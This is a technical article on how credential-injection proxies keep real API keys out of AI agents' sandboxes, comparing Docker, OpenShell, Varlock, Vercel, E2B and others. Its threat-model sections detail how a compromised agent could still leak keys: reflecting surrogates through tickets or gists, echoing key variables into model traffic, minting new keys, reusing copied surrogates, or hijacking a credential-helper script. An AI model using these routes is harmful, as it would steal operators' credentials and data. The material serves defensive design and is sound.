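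Re-signing fails for pre-signed URLs, which carry the signature in the query string so that anyone with the link can fetch a file. The SDK creates the link without contacting AWS, so the proxy can't re-sign it. Anyone the agent sends the link to, whether a colleague or an attacker, gets an error. Varlock also blocks pre-signed URLs that the container tries to open through the proxy.

SigV4 is also common outside AWS. Varlock lists Cloudflare R2, MinIO and Backblaze B2 among the storage services that accept it, so the same signing code can work with them.

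### OpenShell's three signing modes

A signature that covers the body forces the proxy to wait. The signature goes in a header, headers precede the body, and the proxy can't hash the body until it has all of it. The proxy must therefore hold the whole upload in memory before it can forward anything. OpenShell has three modes, which the operator selects separately for each host:

| Mode | Treatment of the body | Intended use |
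|---|---|---|
| `sigv4` | Follows the client's `x-amz-content-sha256` header | Default for most AWS services |
| `sigv4:body` | Holds the body, up to 10 MiB, and signs its hash | Services that require a signed body, such as Bedrock, which hosts AI models |
| `sigv4:no_body` | Streams the body and signs only the headers | Large S3 uploads and chunked transfers |

In the automatic mode, `sigv4`, the proxy uses the client's header to decide whether to sign the body. If the header contains a hash, the proxy buffers the body and signs it. If the header contains `UNSIGNED-PAYLOAD` or the marker for an unsigned stream, the proxy signs only the headers. If the header is missing, the proxy signs the body only when the request declares a length. NVIDIA's example for Bedrock uses this mode.

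In `sigv4:body` mode the proxy rejects bodies over 10 MiB, and NVIDIA recommends either of the other modes for larger ones. The automatic mode probably helps only if the client marks its upload as unsigned, because NVIDIA says this mode handles a hashed body the same way `sigv4:body` does. For an agent that uploads build archives to S3, `sigv4:no_body` is the safer choice.

Leaving the body unsigned adds little risk in this setting. AWS can no longer use the signature to check whether someone altered the body in transit, but TLS still protects it between the proxy and AWS. A signature would not protect against the container anyway, because the container writes the body. The operator does lose the chance to examine a complete upload before the request leaves, since the proxy streams the body through.

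Some clients split a large upload into chunks and sign each one. Aembit, which sells a proxy that injects credentials, calls these "rolling signatures" and says its product can re-sign such uploads. OpenShell can't reproduce the signatures, and NVIDIA advises operators to use `sigv4:no_body` for these clients. Varlock blocks this chunked format whether or not the chunks are signed. Current AWS SDKs use the format for S3 uploads by default, so developers have to change the `requestChecksumCalculation` setting to avoid the block.

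### OAuth logins

The operator can register an API key before the container starts because the key already exists. An OAuth credential comes into being only when somebody logs in. OAuth is the protocol by which a user approves a program's access to an account, usually in a browser. After the approval, the program sends a one-time code to an address at the service called the token endpoint, which returns something like this (the values are invented):

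```
{"access_token":"a-7d20b9f4","refresh_token":"r-c418e06a","expires_in":3600}
```

The access token is a bearer credential that the program sends with each request, like an API key. Here it expires after an hour. The refresh token lasts longer, and the program sends it only to the token endpoint, to get a new access token without asking the user to log in again.

If the agent's program does all this inside the container, it receives both real tokens there in the endpoint's response. It typically saves them in a file so the user doesn't have to log in again. The swap rule can't prevent this, because it changes only requests and the tokens arrive in a response. Docker warned in an earlier version of its documentation that logging in to a third-party agent inside the sandbox would store the real token there, because Docker's proxy did not manage OAuth for those agents.

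Docker runs the login on the host for the agents it supports, including Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex. The user signs in, the proxy manages and refreshes the tokens, and the sandbox receives only a surrogate. Codex prompts the user on the host and Claude Code prompts inside the sandbox, but Docker states that the token never enters the sandbox in either case. It refers to "sentinel masking" of the token response, which suggests that the proxy replaces the real tokens with surrogates before passing the response on.

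To do this, the proxy has to recognise a token exchange and find the tokens in the response. Docker supports only services that return the refresh token in a field called `refresh_token`, and only agents that store their credentials as JSON. It also refuses token exchanges over plain HTTP, at login and at each refresh.

Swapping a header would also not be enough to refresh an access token, because the refresh token is normally sent in the request body. Docker's custom secrets no longer help, because Docker now substitutes them only in chosen headers.

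Developers who package an agent for Docker's sandbox can turn off the masking by setting `passthrough: true`. The real token response then enters the sandbox, where any process that can read the program's memory or its saved login can copy the access and refresh tokens. Losing the refresh token is more serious because a thief may be able to use it elsewhere to get new access tokens until it expires or the user revokes it, even after the operator has deleted the sandbox. Docker says the option reduces isolation but doesn't explain why anyone would want it. A developer might need it for a program that reads information from inside the token, such as the account name, which a surrogate would not contain.

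OpenShell keeps the login out of the sandbox. In NVIDIA's *Refresh Microsoft Graph Credentials with Providers v2*, a tutorial on giving an agent access to a mailbox, the user logs in to Microsoft before starting the tutorial. The gateway stores the refresh token and uses it to renew the access token before it expires. The sandbox has only a surrogate, which stays the same through every renewal.

Support for managed logins varies even within one company's products. Docker's *Authenticate cloud agents*, which covers sandboxes on rented machines rather than the user's own, lists OAuth only for OpenAI. The other agents and model providers it lists need an API key.

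### Git over HTTPS

When Git connects to GitHub over HTTPS, it sends an access token as the password in a Basic authentication header. A proxy that decodes the header can swap the surrogate for the real token as usual. But the real token often covers every branch of several repositories, so the swap would authenticate a push to any of them.

The address of the request doesn't help to tell these pushes apart. Here is a simplified push to an invented repository:

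```
POST /acme/shop.git/git-receive-pack HTTP/1.1

(old commit) (new commit) refs/heads/agent/fix-login
(compressed files)
```

The first line of the HTTP request for a Git push includes the repository, but the branch is in the body. A push to `main` therefore has the same method and path as a push to `agent/fix-login`, so a proxy has to parse Git's own protocol to allow one and refuse the other.

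Anthropic built a proxy of this kind for Claude Code on the web, its service for running the agent on Anthropic's machines. According to Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025), a push goes through these steps:

1. The Git client in the sandbox logs in to the proxy with a scoped credential, which Anthropic created for this purpose.
2. The proxy verifies the credential.
3. The proxy checks the content of the Git operation, including whether the push goes only to the configured branch.
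4. The proxy attaches the real token and sends the request to GitHub.

Unlike an ordinary surrogate, the scoped credential also authenticates the client to the proxy. According to Anthropic, the real credentials stay encrypted on its servers and never enter the session's virtual machine.

Anthropic's *Configure cloud environments* describes the resulting limits. The agent can push only to the session's current working branch, while cloning, fetching and pull requests work normally. Calls to GitHub's API reach only the repositories the user attached to the session, and a setup script gets an error if it tries to download a file from another repository's releases. These are Anthropic's claims about its own service, but anyone with a session can test the branch rule by trying to push to another branch.

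The protection is also limited to GitHub. Anthropic's cloud environments have no dedicated store for other secrets, and Anthropic tells users not to put API keys in environment variables.

### Git over SSH

Git can also connect over SSH, the standard protocol for remote logins, which uses a pair of keys. The service has the public key, and the user proves they have the private key by signing data with it. Many users keep their private keys in an SSH agent, a program that signs data for other programs and is unrelated to AI agents.

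Docker's sandboxes can forward the host's SSH agent into the container. The container gets a socket, a channel through which its programs can reach the SSH agent, and the variable `SSH_AUTH_SOCK` tells them where to find it. A push then works like this:

1. Git in the container opens an SSH connection to GitHub.
2. The SSH client in the container prepares data that is specific to this connection and sends it through the socket.
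3. The SSH agent on the host signs the data with the private key and returns the signature.
4. The client sends the signature to GitHub, which checks it against the public key.

SSH uses no surrogate because it never sends the private key. According to Docker, processes in the sandbox can request signatures but can't read or copy a private key. An attacker therefore can't steal the key, and a captured login signature won't work on any other connection.

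However, the container can request signatures with any key the SSH agent holds while the socket is open. Docker also intends the feature for signing commits, so a compromised container could have its own commits signed in the user's name. Unlike login signatures, commit signatures remain valid after the sandbox is gone.

Forwarding also prevents the branch check, because the data that the SSH agent signs does not name a repository or a branch, and the push travels inside an encrypted connection that begins in the container. Docker's network policy can restrict which SSH servers the container contacts, but not what the container does on them.

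The operator can reduce the risk by pointing Docker's `ssh.agentSocketPath` setting at a separate SSH agent that holds one key with access to one repository, or by switching forwarding off. Forwarding is on by default, though AI agents packaged in Docker's newest format have to request it.

### Checking what a request asks for

The proxy must parse the protocol to re-sign an AWS request, mask an OAuth response or check a Git push, so it can also refuse requests that the real credential would permit. OpenShell's Bedrock example combines the signing mode with a rule that allows only `POST` requests to `/model/*/invoke`. The container can run models through that host, but the proxy refuses all other operations there, even those the AWS key allows.

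NVIDIA's GitHub example applies the same idea to a token. Its policy lets the agent read through GitHub's API but not write. When Claude Code tries to create `hello_world.py` in a repository, the proxy denies the `PUT` request and logs the method, path and rule. It also denies a Git push over HTTPS. The agent therefore has read-only access even if the operator registered a token that can write.

An SSH agent protects the private key at least as well as the proxy protects a token, but it signs data without any information about which operation will follow. Operators may end up with this weaker arrangement because each protocol needs its own code in the proxy and each unsupported variant produces an error. Turning on passthrough or switching from HTTPS to SSH can remove the error, along with the masking or the check that caused it.

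## What a compromised container can still do: reasoning from the design

Suppose an attacker controls everything in the ticket-filing agent's container. The container has the surrogate `k-9b3e70d4c6`, while the real credential, `k-51f0c2e97a`, is in the proxy.

What this attacker can do follows mostly from the design, so anyone can check the reasoning without testing a product. Many of the objections come from two discussions on Hacker News, a forum for programmers. Hacker News' *Deno Sandbox* followed the launch of Deno's sandbox, and the other discussion followed guyb3's *Show HN* (2026), a post introducing OneCLI, an open-source gateway that adds credentials to agents' requests. Most of the commenters used pseudonyms, so readers can judge the objections only by their arguments.

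### The guarantee and its conditions

The design promises that the real credential never enters the container. Outside the container, the credential exists in the proxy, in the store that the proxy reads from, and at the hosts that receive the proxy's requests. The attacker has to get it from one of these, so the promise holds under three conditions:

1. The container cannot read the proxy's memory or files.
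2. The proxy verifies each destination before it inserts the credential.
3. No approved host returns the credential to the container or publishes it.

The container may be able to read the proxy's memory, depending on where the proxy runs. Varlock's proxy runs on the developer's machine, under the same user account as the agent. Varlock warns that a determined agent can start a process outside the proxy and fetch the secrets from their source, so it recommends adding a sandbox, container or virtual machine. Airut's developer, commenting as hardsnow on guyb3's post, said that the proxy has to run outside the sandbox because otherwise the agent can read the keys from the proxy's process.

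Logs need the same care. Gondolin, which runs agents in small virtual machines, lets operators add their own request-handling code. Its *Secrets Handling* warns that this code may run after the swap, so logging the headers can write real credentials to a file. If the operator has shared that file's folder with the agent, the agent can read the credentials.

Fly.io wanted to keep other companies' credentials out of its main web application, so it built Tokenizer. The application would hold only encrypted copies, which Tokenizer would decrypt and add to outgoing requests. But *Tokenized Tokens* explains that, without a limit on destinations, an attacker who took over the application could send a request through Tokenizer to their own server and collect the decrypted credential there. Fly.io therefore made it possible to restrict each secret to a list of hosts.

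This restriction is easy to overlook. Lancetipton, a developer building a similar proxy, said in a comment under guyb3's post that their proxy inserted the credential into any matching request and that they had not thought of limiting each credential to certain hosts. A scope can also be too broad to help. E2B accepts patterns such as `*.com` and warns that they may expose credentials to every matching destination the sandbox contacts.

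The operator has less control over what an approved host does with the credential. Varlock guarantees that a secret goes only to the hosts the operator chose, but says this does not stop one of those hosts from sending it back.

### What a stolen surrogate is worth

If the conditions hold, a stolen surrogate gives no access at any other host. In its launch announcement, Deno calls a surrogate sent to `evil.com` "useless", which is accurate for the credential itself. The surrogate also stops working when the container ends, provided the proxy then deletes its record of the surrogate.

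The time limit matters because an operator may discover a theft late. Vercel points out that malicious code can copy a real bearer key to another service and use it long after the sandbox has stopped. Suppose the container runs for twenty minutes and the operator learns of the attack a week later. A thief could have used the real key from any machine for that whole week, but could have used a surrogate only during those twenty minutes, and the operator can check the proxy's log to see how it was used.

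In the Deno discussion on Hacker News, simonw compared this to HttpOnly cookies. A browser attaches such a cookie to requests made by a page's scripts but does not let the scripts read it. An attacker who gets a script into the page can therefore act as the user while the page is open, but cannot copy the cookie for use elsewhere.

The time limit is weaker when the surrogate is an encrypted token. Tokenizer is stateless, so it has no record to delete when a container ends. A copied token works for anyone who can reach the proxy and authenticate to it, until the operator replaces the real credential or the proxy's decryption key. The token itself would need an expiry date to prevent this.

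A surrogate can also reveal something to whoever receives it. microsandbox, another sandboxing tool, gives the container a surrogate named after the variable, such as `$MSB_OPENAI_API_KEY`. This makes logs easier to read, but as microsandbox's *Sandboxes that lie about their secrets* acknowledges, it also advertises which credentials the container can use. The operator can therefore choose what happens when a surrogate is on its way to an unapproved host:

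| Response | Example |
|---|---|
| Forward the surrogate unchanged | A monitoring tool uploads a record of the session, which happens to include the surrogate |
| Block the request | A planted instruction tells the agent to post the surrogate to an unknown site |
| End the sandbox | An install script sends the surrogate to an unknown host while building a software release |

Ending the sandbox makes sense in the last case because the build is now suspect. A surrogate in the wrong place is a useful alarm, but a text search would miss it if the attacker encoded it first. Surrogates can also cause false alarms. Commenting on guyb3's post, anthonyskipper objected that fake keys would trigger the scanners companies use to find leaked keys in their repositories.

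### Permitted actions at approved hosts

An attacker can use a credential without stealing it. Commenting on guyb3's post, paxys argued that an agent with a dummy key can do exactly what it could have done with the real one, and that the proxy may give a false sense of security. ipince argued that an attacker who can persuade an agent to give away its key can also persuade it to use the service on their behalf. skywhopper thought that leaked credentials were not the biggest risk, since an agent that can make arbitrary calls can still run up costs or delete production systems.

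The objection is right about what the attacker can do while the container is running. But the access ends when the container stops, and every use passes through a proxy that can log or refuse it. These limits help a lot with a key to a model provider, which a thief might otherwise use for months at the owner's expense, but very little with a key that can delete a database, because the attacker needs only one request.

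In *What a Credential Vault Can and Can't Do for AI Agent Security*, Fishner concedes on OneCLI's behalf that the product protects against theft of credentials and that misuse requires other controls. For example, if an operator gives an agent access to Stripe, a payment company, and the agent creates an unwanted charge, OneCLI adds the Stripe key and the charge goes through. The concession is believable because a vendor gains little by understating what its product can do.

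**Method and path rules**, like the one in OpenShell's Bedrock example, could limit the ticket agent to `POST /v1/tickets`. The agent could then file tickets but not delete them or read the ones customers have filed. Vercel can also match a request's query and headers before it injects a credential.

Such rules work only if the method and path reveal what the request does. In GraphQL, a query language that many services offer, reads and writes usually go to the same path, with the operation in the body. An interface that accepts database queries has the same problem. In the Deno discussion on Hacker News, ryanrasti therefore suggested constraining the queries themselves, so that sandboxed code could request only one customer's data. A path rule also cannot distinguish a useful ticket from one the attacker wrote to mislead the support team.

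**Narrowing permissions at the provider** is usually a better first step. The ticket service records which tickets belong to which project, so it can enforce distinctions that do not appear in a web address. Its restrictions also still apply if the proxy has a bug or the attacker gets the real key. Vercel recommends limiting injected credentials to the operations the workload needs. However, the operator can only choose from the permissions the provider offers, and some services offer only a single key with full access.

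**Human approval** suits rare, serious actions such as refunds. Fishner proposes holding certain requests, selected by host, path, method and agent, until a person approves them. The approver needs to see the whole request, because a compromised container writes both the request and any accompanying explanation. Asking for approval too often is risky because people may start approving requests without reading them.

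Rate limits reduce the damage without requiring anyone's attention. Fishner's example is an agent that makes a hundred Stripe calls in a minute, which the gateway could cut off. A rate limit doesn't stop the first few calls, so it is more useful against high costs and bulk copying than against a single destructive request.

The operator can also withdraw the credential partway through a job. In an example from Vercel, the sandbox clones private repositories while the firewall adds a GitHub token. The operator then switches the policy to `deny-all` before any untrusted code runs. That code can read the cloned files but can't use the token or send the files over the network. This only works when the job can be split into phases, which would be hard for a coding agent that alternates between reading tickets and running code.

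On some services, a client can use its key to create more keys, and the service returns each new key in the response. An attacker in the container can therefore obtain a real credential, even though the original never leaves the proxy, and use it from another machine after the container has ended. Adding a new user to the account or registering a new SSH key has much the same effect. The operator should use a credential without these permissions or, if that isn't possible, have the proxy refuse the requests.

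The attacker can also misuse read access. If the agent has permission to read tickets, the attacker can have it collect customers' names and complaints and send them elsewhere. In a comment on guyb3's post, c5huracan noted that a proxy prevents key leakage but not the exfiltration of data that the agent reads through it. Whether the data can get out depends on the network allowlist, which some products leave open. Deno, for example, allows all outbound requests unless the operator supplies a list.

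### Getting the real key from an approved host

An attacker may also be able to make an approved host reveal the credential. In the Deno discussion on Hacker News, ptx assumed that the proxy would replace the surrogate wherever it appeared in a request. If it did, an attacker would only need an approved host that repeats what it receives, such as a page that asks for a name and answers with a greeting.

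The ticket service would do. If the container files a ticket with the surrogate as its title, a proxy of this kind puts the real key in the title:

| Step | Title of the ticket |
|---|---|
| Container files the ticket | `k-9b3e70d4c6` |
| Proxy swaps the surrogate and forwards the request | `k-51f0c2e97a` |
| Ticket service stores the ticket | `k-51f0c2e97a` |
| Container asks to see the ticket | `k-51f0c2e97a` |

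The service is working as it should, because nothing marks a title as secret. Commenters on Hacker News gave other examples, including an error message that repeats an unknown user's name and any setting that a program can write and later read back. One commenter said this was effectively what happened in a vulnerability at BotGhost, a service for building chat bots.

The key can leak even if the host sends no response to the container. On Hacker News, saghm pointed out that a malicious program could put the surrogate in the text of a public gist, a snippet shared on GitHub. The proxy would replace the surrogate with the real key, which anyone could then read on GitHub's website.

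An agent can also expose the real key without any unusual feature at the host. If it runs `echo $OPENAI_API_KEY`, the surrogate becomes part of the conversation, which the agent sends to OpenAI with its next request. Because OpenAI's host is in the surrogate's scope, a proxy that edits request bodies would put the real key into the text the model reads, and the model could repeat it in its answer. This would also happen by accident whenever the surrogate appeared in a command's output. Hacker News user its-summertime raised this problem, and simonw replied that the proxy only makes the swap for the configured host. That does not answer the objection, because the request is going to that host.

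tptacek, who spoke on Hacker News as one of the people behind Tokenizer, called the question of where in a request the proxy makes the swap "the big bug class" of this design. He said that Tokenizer restricts the swap to approved headers.

**Substituting only in named headers** removes most of the problem. In the ticket example, the proxy would replace the surrogate in the `Authorization` header but not the one in the title. Services treat that header as secret and seldom store or repeat it. By default, Gondolin and microsandbox substitute in headers but not in the body. Deno's behaviour is less clear. lucacasonato, who answered for Deno on Hacker News, said it replaces secrets only in headers, but a reply in another copy of the discussion said it also replaces them in URLs and bodies.

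The operator should specify the headers in which the proxy may make the swap, because allowing it in every header can expose the real key. Some services record the `User-Agent` header, which identifies the client program, and display it in a list of recent logins. If the proxy makes the swap there, the container may be able to read the key from that list. HTTP Basic authentication carries a similar risk, because Gondolin replaces a surrogate in either the user name or the password. If the surrogate is in the user name and the service includes that name in a "no such user" error, the response would contain the real key.

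*Tokenizer* (2023) describes a stricter rule, in which the encrypted secret can list the headers that may carry the credential and the text that may surround it, such as `Bearer` followed by a space. The client can choose only from those lists. This comes close to header injection. ptx thought header injection was safer and simpler than searching for a surrogate because the proxy alone decides where the credential goes.

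Both approaches exclude services that expect a credential in the request body, but some vendors support them. Blaxel's *Proxy secrets injection* describes a proxy that resolves secret names in the headers and bodies of requests from sandboxed code. An operator who needs substitution in bodies should limit it to the one path that requires it, such as a login endpoint, if the product allows.

**Scrubbing responses** is the reverse of the swap. The proxy searches each response for the real credential and replaces it with the surrogate before the container receives it. Varlock does this but does not treat it as a security boundary, and gives its reasons:

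- It scans only text responses that are uncompressed and no larger than 2 MB.
- The container can ask the service for a compressed response, which the proxy will not scan.
- It looks for an exact match, so it misses a copy that the service has shortened, escaped or encoded.

A proxy could remove the container's request for compression, but it could not anticipate every way of rewriting a string. A model is especially flexible, since it can print half a key or spell it backwards. Scrubbing also does not protect against the public gist, because the attacker can read it from another machine without the response passing through the proxy.

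Scrubbing still helps with accidents, such as an error page that repeats the request's headers, but it should not be the reason for trusting a host. Varlock advises operators to bind a secret only to hosts they trust not to return it. It considers reflection rare among real APIs. This is plausible for the `Authorization` header, but Varlock cites no measurements.

### Using a copied surrogate from another machine

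A copied surrogate is useless to an attacker who cannot reach the proxy, but the attacker may control another machine that can. In a comment on guyb3's post, morphology described a malicious agent that obtains an honest agent's surrogate and presents it to the same gateway, which cannot distinguish the two agents. dingdingdang replied that the surrogate works only on the local network. morphology agreed, but added that the operator then has to make sure no untrusted agent can join that network.

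The danger is greatest when one proxy serves several containers. Suppose a company runs two agents behind the same proxy, one that files tickets and one that makes payments. If the proxy accepts any surrogate from any container, the ticket agent could make payments with a copy of the payment agent's surrogate. Copies may appear in shared logs because people regard surrogates as harmless. In the Deno discussion on Hacker News, a commenter described this as a confused deputy problem, in which the proxy checks a credential's destination but not who is making the request.

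Many gateways therefore require a password. In an example from OneCLI, an agent's surrogate is `FAKE_KEY`, which doesn't identify the agent, so the gateway has to do that another way. According to Fishner, each agent has its own access token for the gateway, and an operator can revoke a compromised agent's token while the others continue. *Tokenizer* uses a similar scheme, in which each encrypted secret specifies how the client must authenticate.

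A password stops someone who has only the surrogate, but not someone who has compromised the container. The agent must be able to read the password to send it, so, as morphology pointed out, the attacker can copy both the password and the surrogate.

The proxy can identify a container more safely by something that cannot be copied, such as the connection its requests arrive on. Anthropic describes a container that has no network at all and reaches the proxy through a Unix socket, a special file that connects programs on the same machine. If each container has its own socket, the socket identifies which container sent a request. Docker's *Network policies* describes a similar separation, with one filtering proxy for each sandbox. The proxy can then swap a surrogate for the real key only when the request comes from the container that received that surrogate.

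When the proxy is on a different machine, a trusted program beside the container can authenticate the container to the proxy. morphology proposed a helper process, or sidecar, that connects to the gateway with mutual TLS, in which both sides present certificates. The agent cannot access the sidecar's private key, so it cannot leak it. Similarly, when Vercel's firewall forwards requests to a customer's own proxy, it adds a token that identifies the sandbox, which the proxy can use to control what that sandbox may do.

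Even if the surrogate is tied to a container, an attacker can still use it by sending the container instructions from outside, having it make requests and collecting the results. This requires a two-way channel, which a strict allowlist makes harder to find, and the attacker loses this access when the container stops.

### Hosts that serve many customers

A host name is a coarse way to describe what an agent should reach. GitHub's API serves the operator's repositories and everyone else's from a single host. Consider two requests to comment on an issue, the first in the operator's repository and the second in a stranger's (both are invented):

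```
POST https://api.github.com/repos/acme/shop/issues/12/comments
POST https://api.github.com/repos/stranger/notes/issues/3/comments
```

Both requests pass the allowlist and fall within the GitHub token's host scope, so the proxy authenticates both. If the token allows commenting on other people's repositories, a compromised container can put source code or customer data in the second comment, where the stranger can read it. Docker warns that allowing a broad domain such as `github.com` permits access to everything on it, including other users' content, and that agents could use this access to send data out. The same access can also expose the agent to instructions from strangers, because it may read their comments.

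A path rule that allows only `/repos/acme/` would block the second request, and so would GitHub if the token covered only the operator's repositories. Neither restriction is enough if `acme/shop` is public, because the stranger can read comments there too. The operator would have to keep the agent away from public repositories, or have someone approve what it writes in them.

Some services can also make requests on a client's behalf, for example by fetching an image from an address in a document. Anthropic advises operators who give an agent broad credentials for an allowed domain to ensure that the agent cannot use that domain to trigger other network requests or send data out. Operators need some knowledge of the service to check this, because the proxy receives only the request to the approved host. Cloud storage is easier to restrict when each customer's bucket has its own host name,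 as in the S3 example of the previous section. The operator can then approve `examplebucket.s3.amazonaws.com` alone, whereas a pattern such as `*.amazonaws.com` would also allow requests to other customers' buckets.

A shared host also allows the container to use somebody else's account. In the case that Haulos described, the agent uploads files with the attacker's own Anthropic key, which the swap does not affect. Header injection can prevent this if the proxy overwrites whatever the container sent. Vercel does so, and gives as its reason that sandboxed code should not be able to substitute its own credentials. The two designs compare as follows:

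| What the container puts in the header | Proxy that only swaps surrogates | Proxy that overwrites the header |
|---|---|---|
| The surrogate | Request goes to the operator's account | Request goes to the operator's account |
| The attacker's key | Request goes to the attacker's account | Request goes to the operator's account |
| Nothing | Request has no credential | Request goes to the operator's account |

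With overwriting, the uploaded files end up in the operator's account, where the attacker normally can't read them. But the proxy must also remove keys from every other place where the service accepts them, such as a second header or the web address. Overwriting works only at hosts for which the operator has written a rule, and it does not stop the agent from publishing something under the operator's name.

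Overwriting the credential header on every matching request adds the operator's authority even to requests that don't need it. With surrogates, a program can request a public file without sending a credential. Path rules can reduce this unneeded authority, and dropping unrecognised credentials, as Airut does, avoids it altogether.

### Attacker aims and the controls that stop them

Some attacks have nothing to do with credentials. A compromised container can delete the agent's files or, less noticeably, add a flaw to the code the agent delivers, and the proxy then authenticates the push like any other. Fishner lists damage done through a shell among the things OneCLI does not prevent. The table below includes both these attacks and those that involve the credential.

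| Attacker's aim | Does the surrogate design stop it? | Further control |
|---|---|---|
| Read the real credential in the container | Yes, if the operator has left no other copy there | Keep `.env` files and other stored secrets out of the container |
| Read the credential from the proxy | Only if the proxy runs where the container cannot reach its memory or logs | Run the proxy outside the sandbox, under another account or on another machine |
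| Send the credential to an unapproved host | Yes, if the proxy verifies destinations | Narrow host scopes without broad patterns |
| Use the credential after the container ends | Yes, if the proxy deletes the surrogate's record | Expiry dates for encrypted tokens |
| Create a new key through the service | No | A credential without that permission, or a rule that blocks the request |
| Misuse the credential at an approved host | No | Narrower provider permissions, method and path rules, human approval, rate limits |
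| Make an approved host return or publish the credential | No | Substitution only in named headers, or header injection; response scrubbing catches some accidents |
| Use a copied surrogate from another machine | Only if that machine cannot reach the proxy | Tie each surrogate to one container or network path |
| Send other data to an unapproved host | No | A network allowlist |
| Send data through an approved host with many customers | No | Path rules, tokens limited to private projects, approval of public posts |
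| Upload data with the attacker's own key | No | Overwrite the authentication header, or drop unrecognised credentials |
| Tamper with the code that the agent delivers | No | Human review, and discarding the output of a compromised container |

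## How shipped systems differ, according to their documentation

Products differ considerably in the controls they offer operators. This comparison relies on the manuals, command references, announcements and release notes that vendors and developers publish about their own systems. These documents are good evidence of intended behaviour, and are often specific enough to check with a single request, but they are poor evidence that the behaviour holds under attack.

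Docker's release notes show that real credentials entered sandboxes designed to keep them out. On 24 July 2026, Docker introduced SSH access so that developers could connect to its sandboxes from an editor. Five days later, Docker (2026) issued a fix because SSH sessions were forwarding variables such as `ANTHROPIC_API_KEY` and `GH_TOKEN` from the developer's machine into the sandbox by default. A release on 6 August stopped sessions from Claude Desktop, Anthropic's desktop application, from exposing OAuth access tokens in the sandbox. Nothing in the notes suggests that the proxy had failed. The real keys bypassed it, so even an accurate description of the proxy would not have revealed the problem.

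Details of several features below may change because Docker's custom secrets are experimental, E2B's header rules are in public beta, and Infisical's newest product is in preview.

### What the proxy changes in a request

Docker supplies keys in two ways. For eleven common services, including Anthropic, OpenAI and GitHub, its proxy writes the authentication header itself. The container typically holds only the word `proxy-managed`, so programs that require a key at startup can still run. For other services, the user can register a custom secret, and the proxy replaces a surrogate with the real credential.

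Docker has narrowed that swap during 2026. In documentation from about August, Docker stated that the proxy replaced the surrogate anywhere in a request, and suggested custom secrets for services that expect a key in the body. According to the current documentation, the proxy makes the swap only in chosen headers, and only over HTTPS. For the ticket service, the command would now be:

```
printf '%s' "$REAL_KEY" | sbx secret set-custom \
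    --host api.tickets.example --env TICKET_KEY \
    --header Authorization --value-stdin
```

If the agent puts its surrogate in a ticket's title, the service now receives the surrogate instead of the real key, so it cannot repeat the real key when it returns the title. However, custom secrets no longer work with a service that reads the key from the request body. Without the `--header` option, the proxy uses a default list of headers from Docker's settings.

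The last option reads the key from standard input. Docker (2026) added this method on 3 November and warns that the earlier form, `--value "$REAL_KEY"`, exposes the key in the command's arguments, which other processes on the machine may be able to read.

Docker also filters responses to requests in which it has inserted a custom secret. It masks the real value wherever it finds it in the headers or body, including copies in base64, percent-encoding or escaped JSON. This catches more than Varlock's search for exact matches, but it also causes more errors because the proxy refuses partial responses and unsupported content encodings. For example, a client that resumes an interrupted download gets a `502` error. Docker acknowledges that a service could still return the secret in pieces, and that the filter doesn't inspect WebSocket messages. Custom secrets must have at least eight characters,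 presumably so that the filter doesn't mask ordinary text.

Vercel, Cloudflare and E2B set request headers instead of swapping surrogates for real keys. On Vercel, an operator lists a domain and the headers for requests to it, and the firewall adds those headers or replaces the ones the program sent. The program needs a surrogate only if it won't run without a key.

However, a proxy that chooses a credential by host has trouble when a program needs two for the same host. Suppose the ticket agent has one key for reading tickets and another for filing them. A script using surrogates selects a key by sending the matching surrogate, but with header injection, nothing in the request identifies which key to use, and E2B applies only one rule to each request. The operator could use a single key with both permissions, but then every request would have more authority than it needs.

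Cloudflare's approach is flexible enough to avoid this. *Secure credential injection and dynamic egress policies for Sandboxes* describes outbound Workers, small programs that run outside the sandbox and can modify its requests. An operator could write a Worker that uses the reading key for `GET` and the filing key for `POST`, but would then also be responsible for the security checks. Workers handle both HTTP and HTTPS, and Cloudflare's example adds a credential to requests for `github.com` without checking the protocol. An operator who copies the example should add that check, because otherwise a plain HTTP request might carry the credential unencrypted.

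Header injection can also fail without an obvious error. According to E2B's *Injecting secrets into requests*, if a rule refers to a secret that the operator has deleted or misspelled, the proxy drops the whole header and still forwards the request. The ticket service would probably return a `401` error, but a service that accepts anonymous requests might return only public data, which the agent could mistake for a complete answer. An attacker can't use this failure to insert their own key in that header, because the proxy also removes any value the container set for it.

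Blaxel can write fields into a request's JSON body, which helps with services that don't read credentials from headers. This is safer than searching the body for a surrogate, because the operator chooses the field. The credential can still be exposed if the service later returns that field. Blaxel doesn't recommend the feature for production use.

Infisical supports both header injection and surrogates, and requires the agent to identify itself to the proxy first. Infisical's current product gives the agent a session token that expires. The token covers one "access bundle", a list of services with a credential for each. The agent can send a surrogate where a program expects a key, and elsewhere the proxy adds the header. Infisical's earlier Agent Proxy used identity tokens for the same purpose and, according to Infisical, rejected any request without a valid token before doing anything else.

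A compromised agent can read its session token, but the token gives access only to the services in its bundle, and an operator can revoke it. Revocation reaches a running agent within 60 seconds by default, which is much sooner than a long session would expire but still leaves an attacker time to do a lot.

Docker's documentation is less clear about sandboxes on rented cloud machines. According to Docker's *sbx secret set-custom*, the cloud proxy sets a header on requests to the chosen hosts instead of replacing the surrogate. But Docker also tells cloud users to copy a generated surrogate into their client, and states that the proxy substitutes the real value for it. A user could find out which description is correct by sending a request without a surrogate. The proxy would authenticate that request only if it sets the header.

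### Where the real credential is stored

For sandboxes on the user's own machine, Docker stores credentials in the operating system's keychain, which is Keychain on macOS, Credential Manager on Windows and the desktop environment's keyring on Linux. A keychain can control access separately for each application. Linux servers often have no desktop keyring, so Docker falls back to a file protected only by file permissions. An agent running unattended on a server is therefore more likely to depend on this weaker storage than one running on a laptop.

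Docker can also store a reference to the credential instead of the credential itself. The reference might point to an entry in a password manager, or it might be a command that prints the secret:

```
sbx secret set github --command 'gh auth token'
```

When the proxy needs the token, Docker runs the command on the host and, by default, caches the result for 55 minutes. This avoids a second stored copy, but it can let an attacker escape the sandbox. For example, if a user registers `./credential-helper`, a script in a project folder that the sandbox can write to, a compromised container could replace the script with its own code. The host would then run that code outside the sandbox at the next refresh.

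Docker now runs these commands from a new temporary directory, so a relative path like this one no longer resolves to a file in the project. Users still have to keep the script, and any code or configuration it loads, outside folders the sandbox can write to. Docker does not inspect the script's dependencies or restrict what the script does.

Wherever the credential is stored, the proxy must load it into memory to use it, and a crash report can contain a copy of that memory. Docker therefore excludes its background process from Windows error reporting.

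Hosted platforms store the credential on their own servers or receive it when a sandbox starts. In the examples from Deno and Vercel, the operator's application reads the key from an environment variable and passes it to the platform. The application runs on a server that doesn't run the agent's commands, but an attacker who compromises that server can still read the key.

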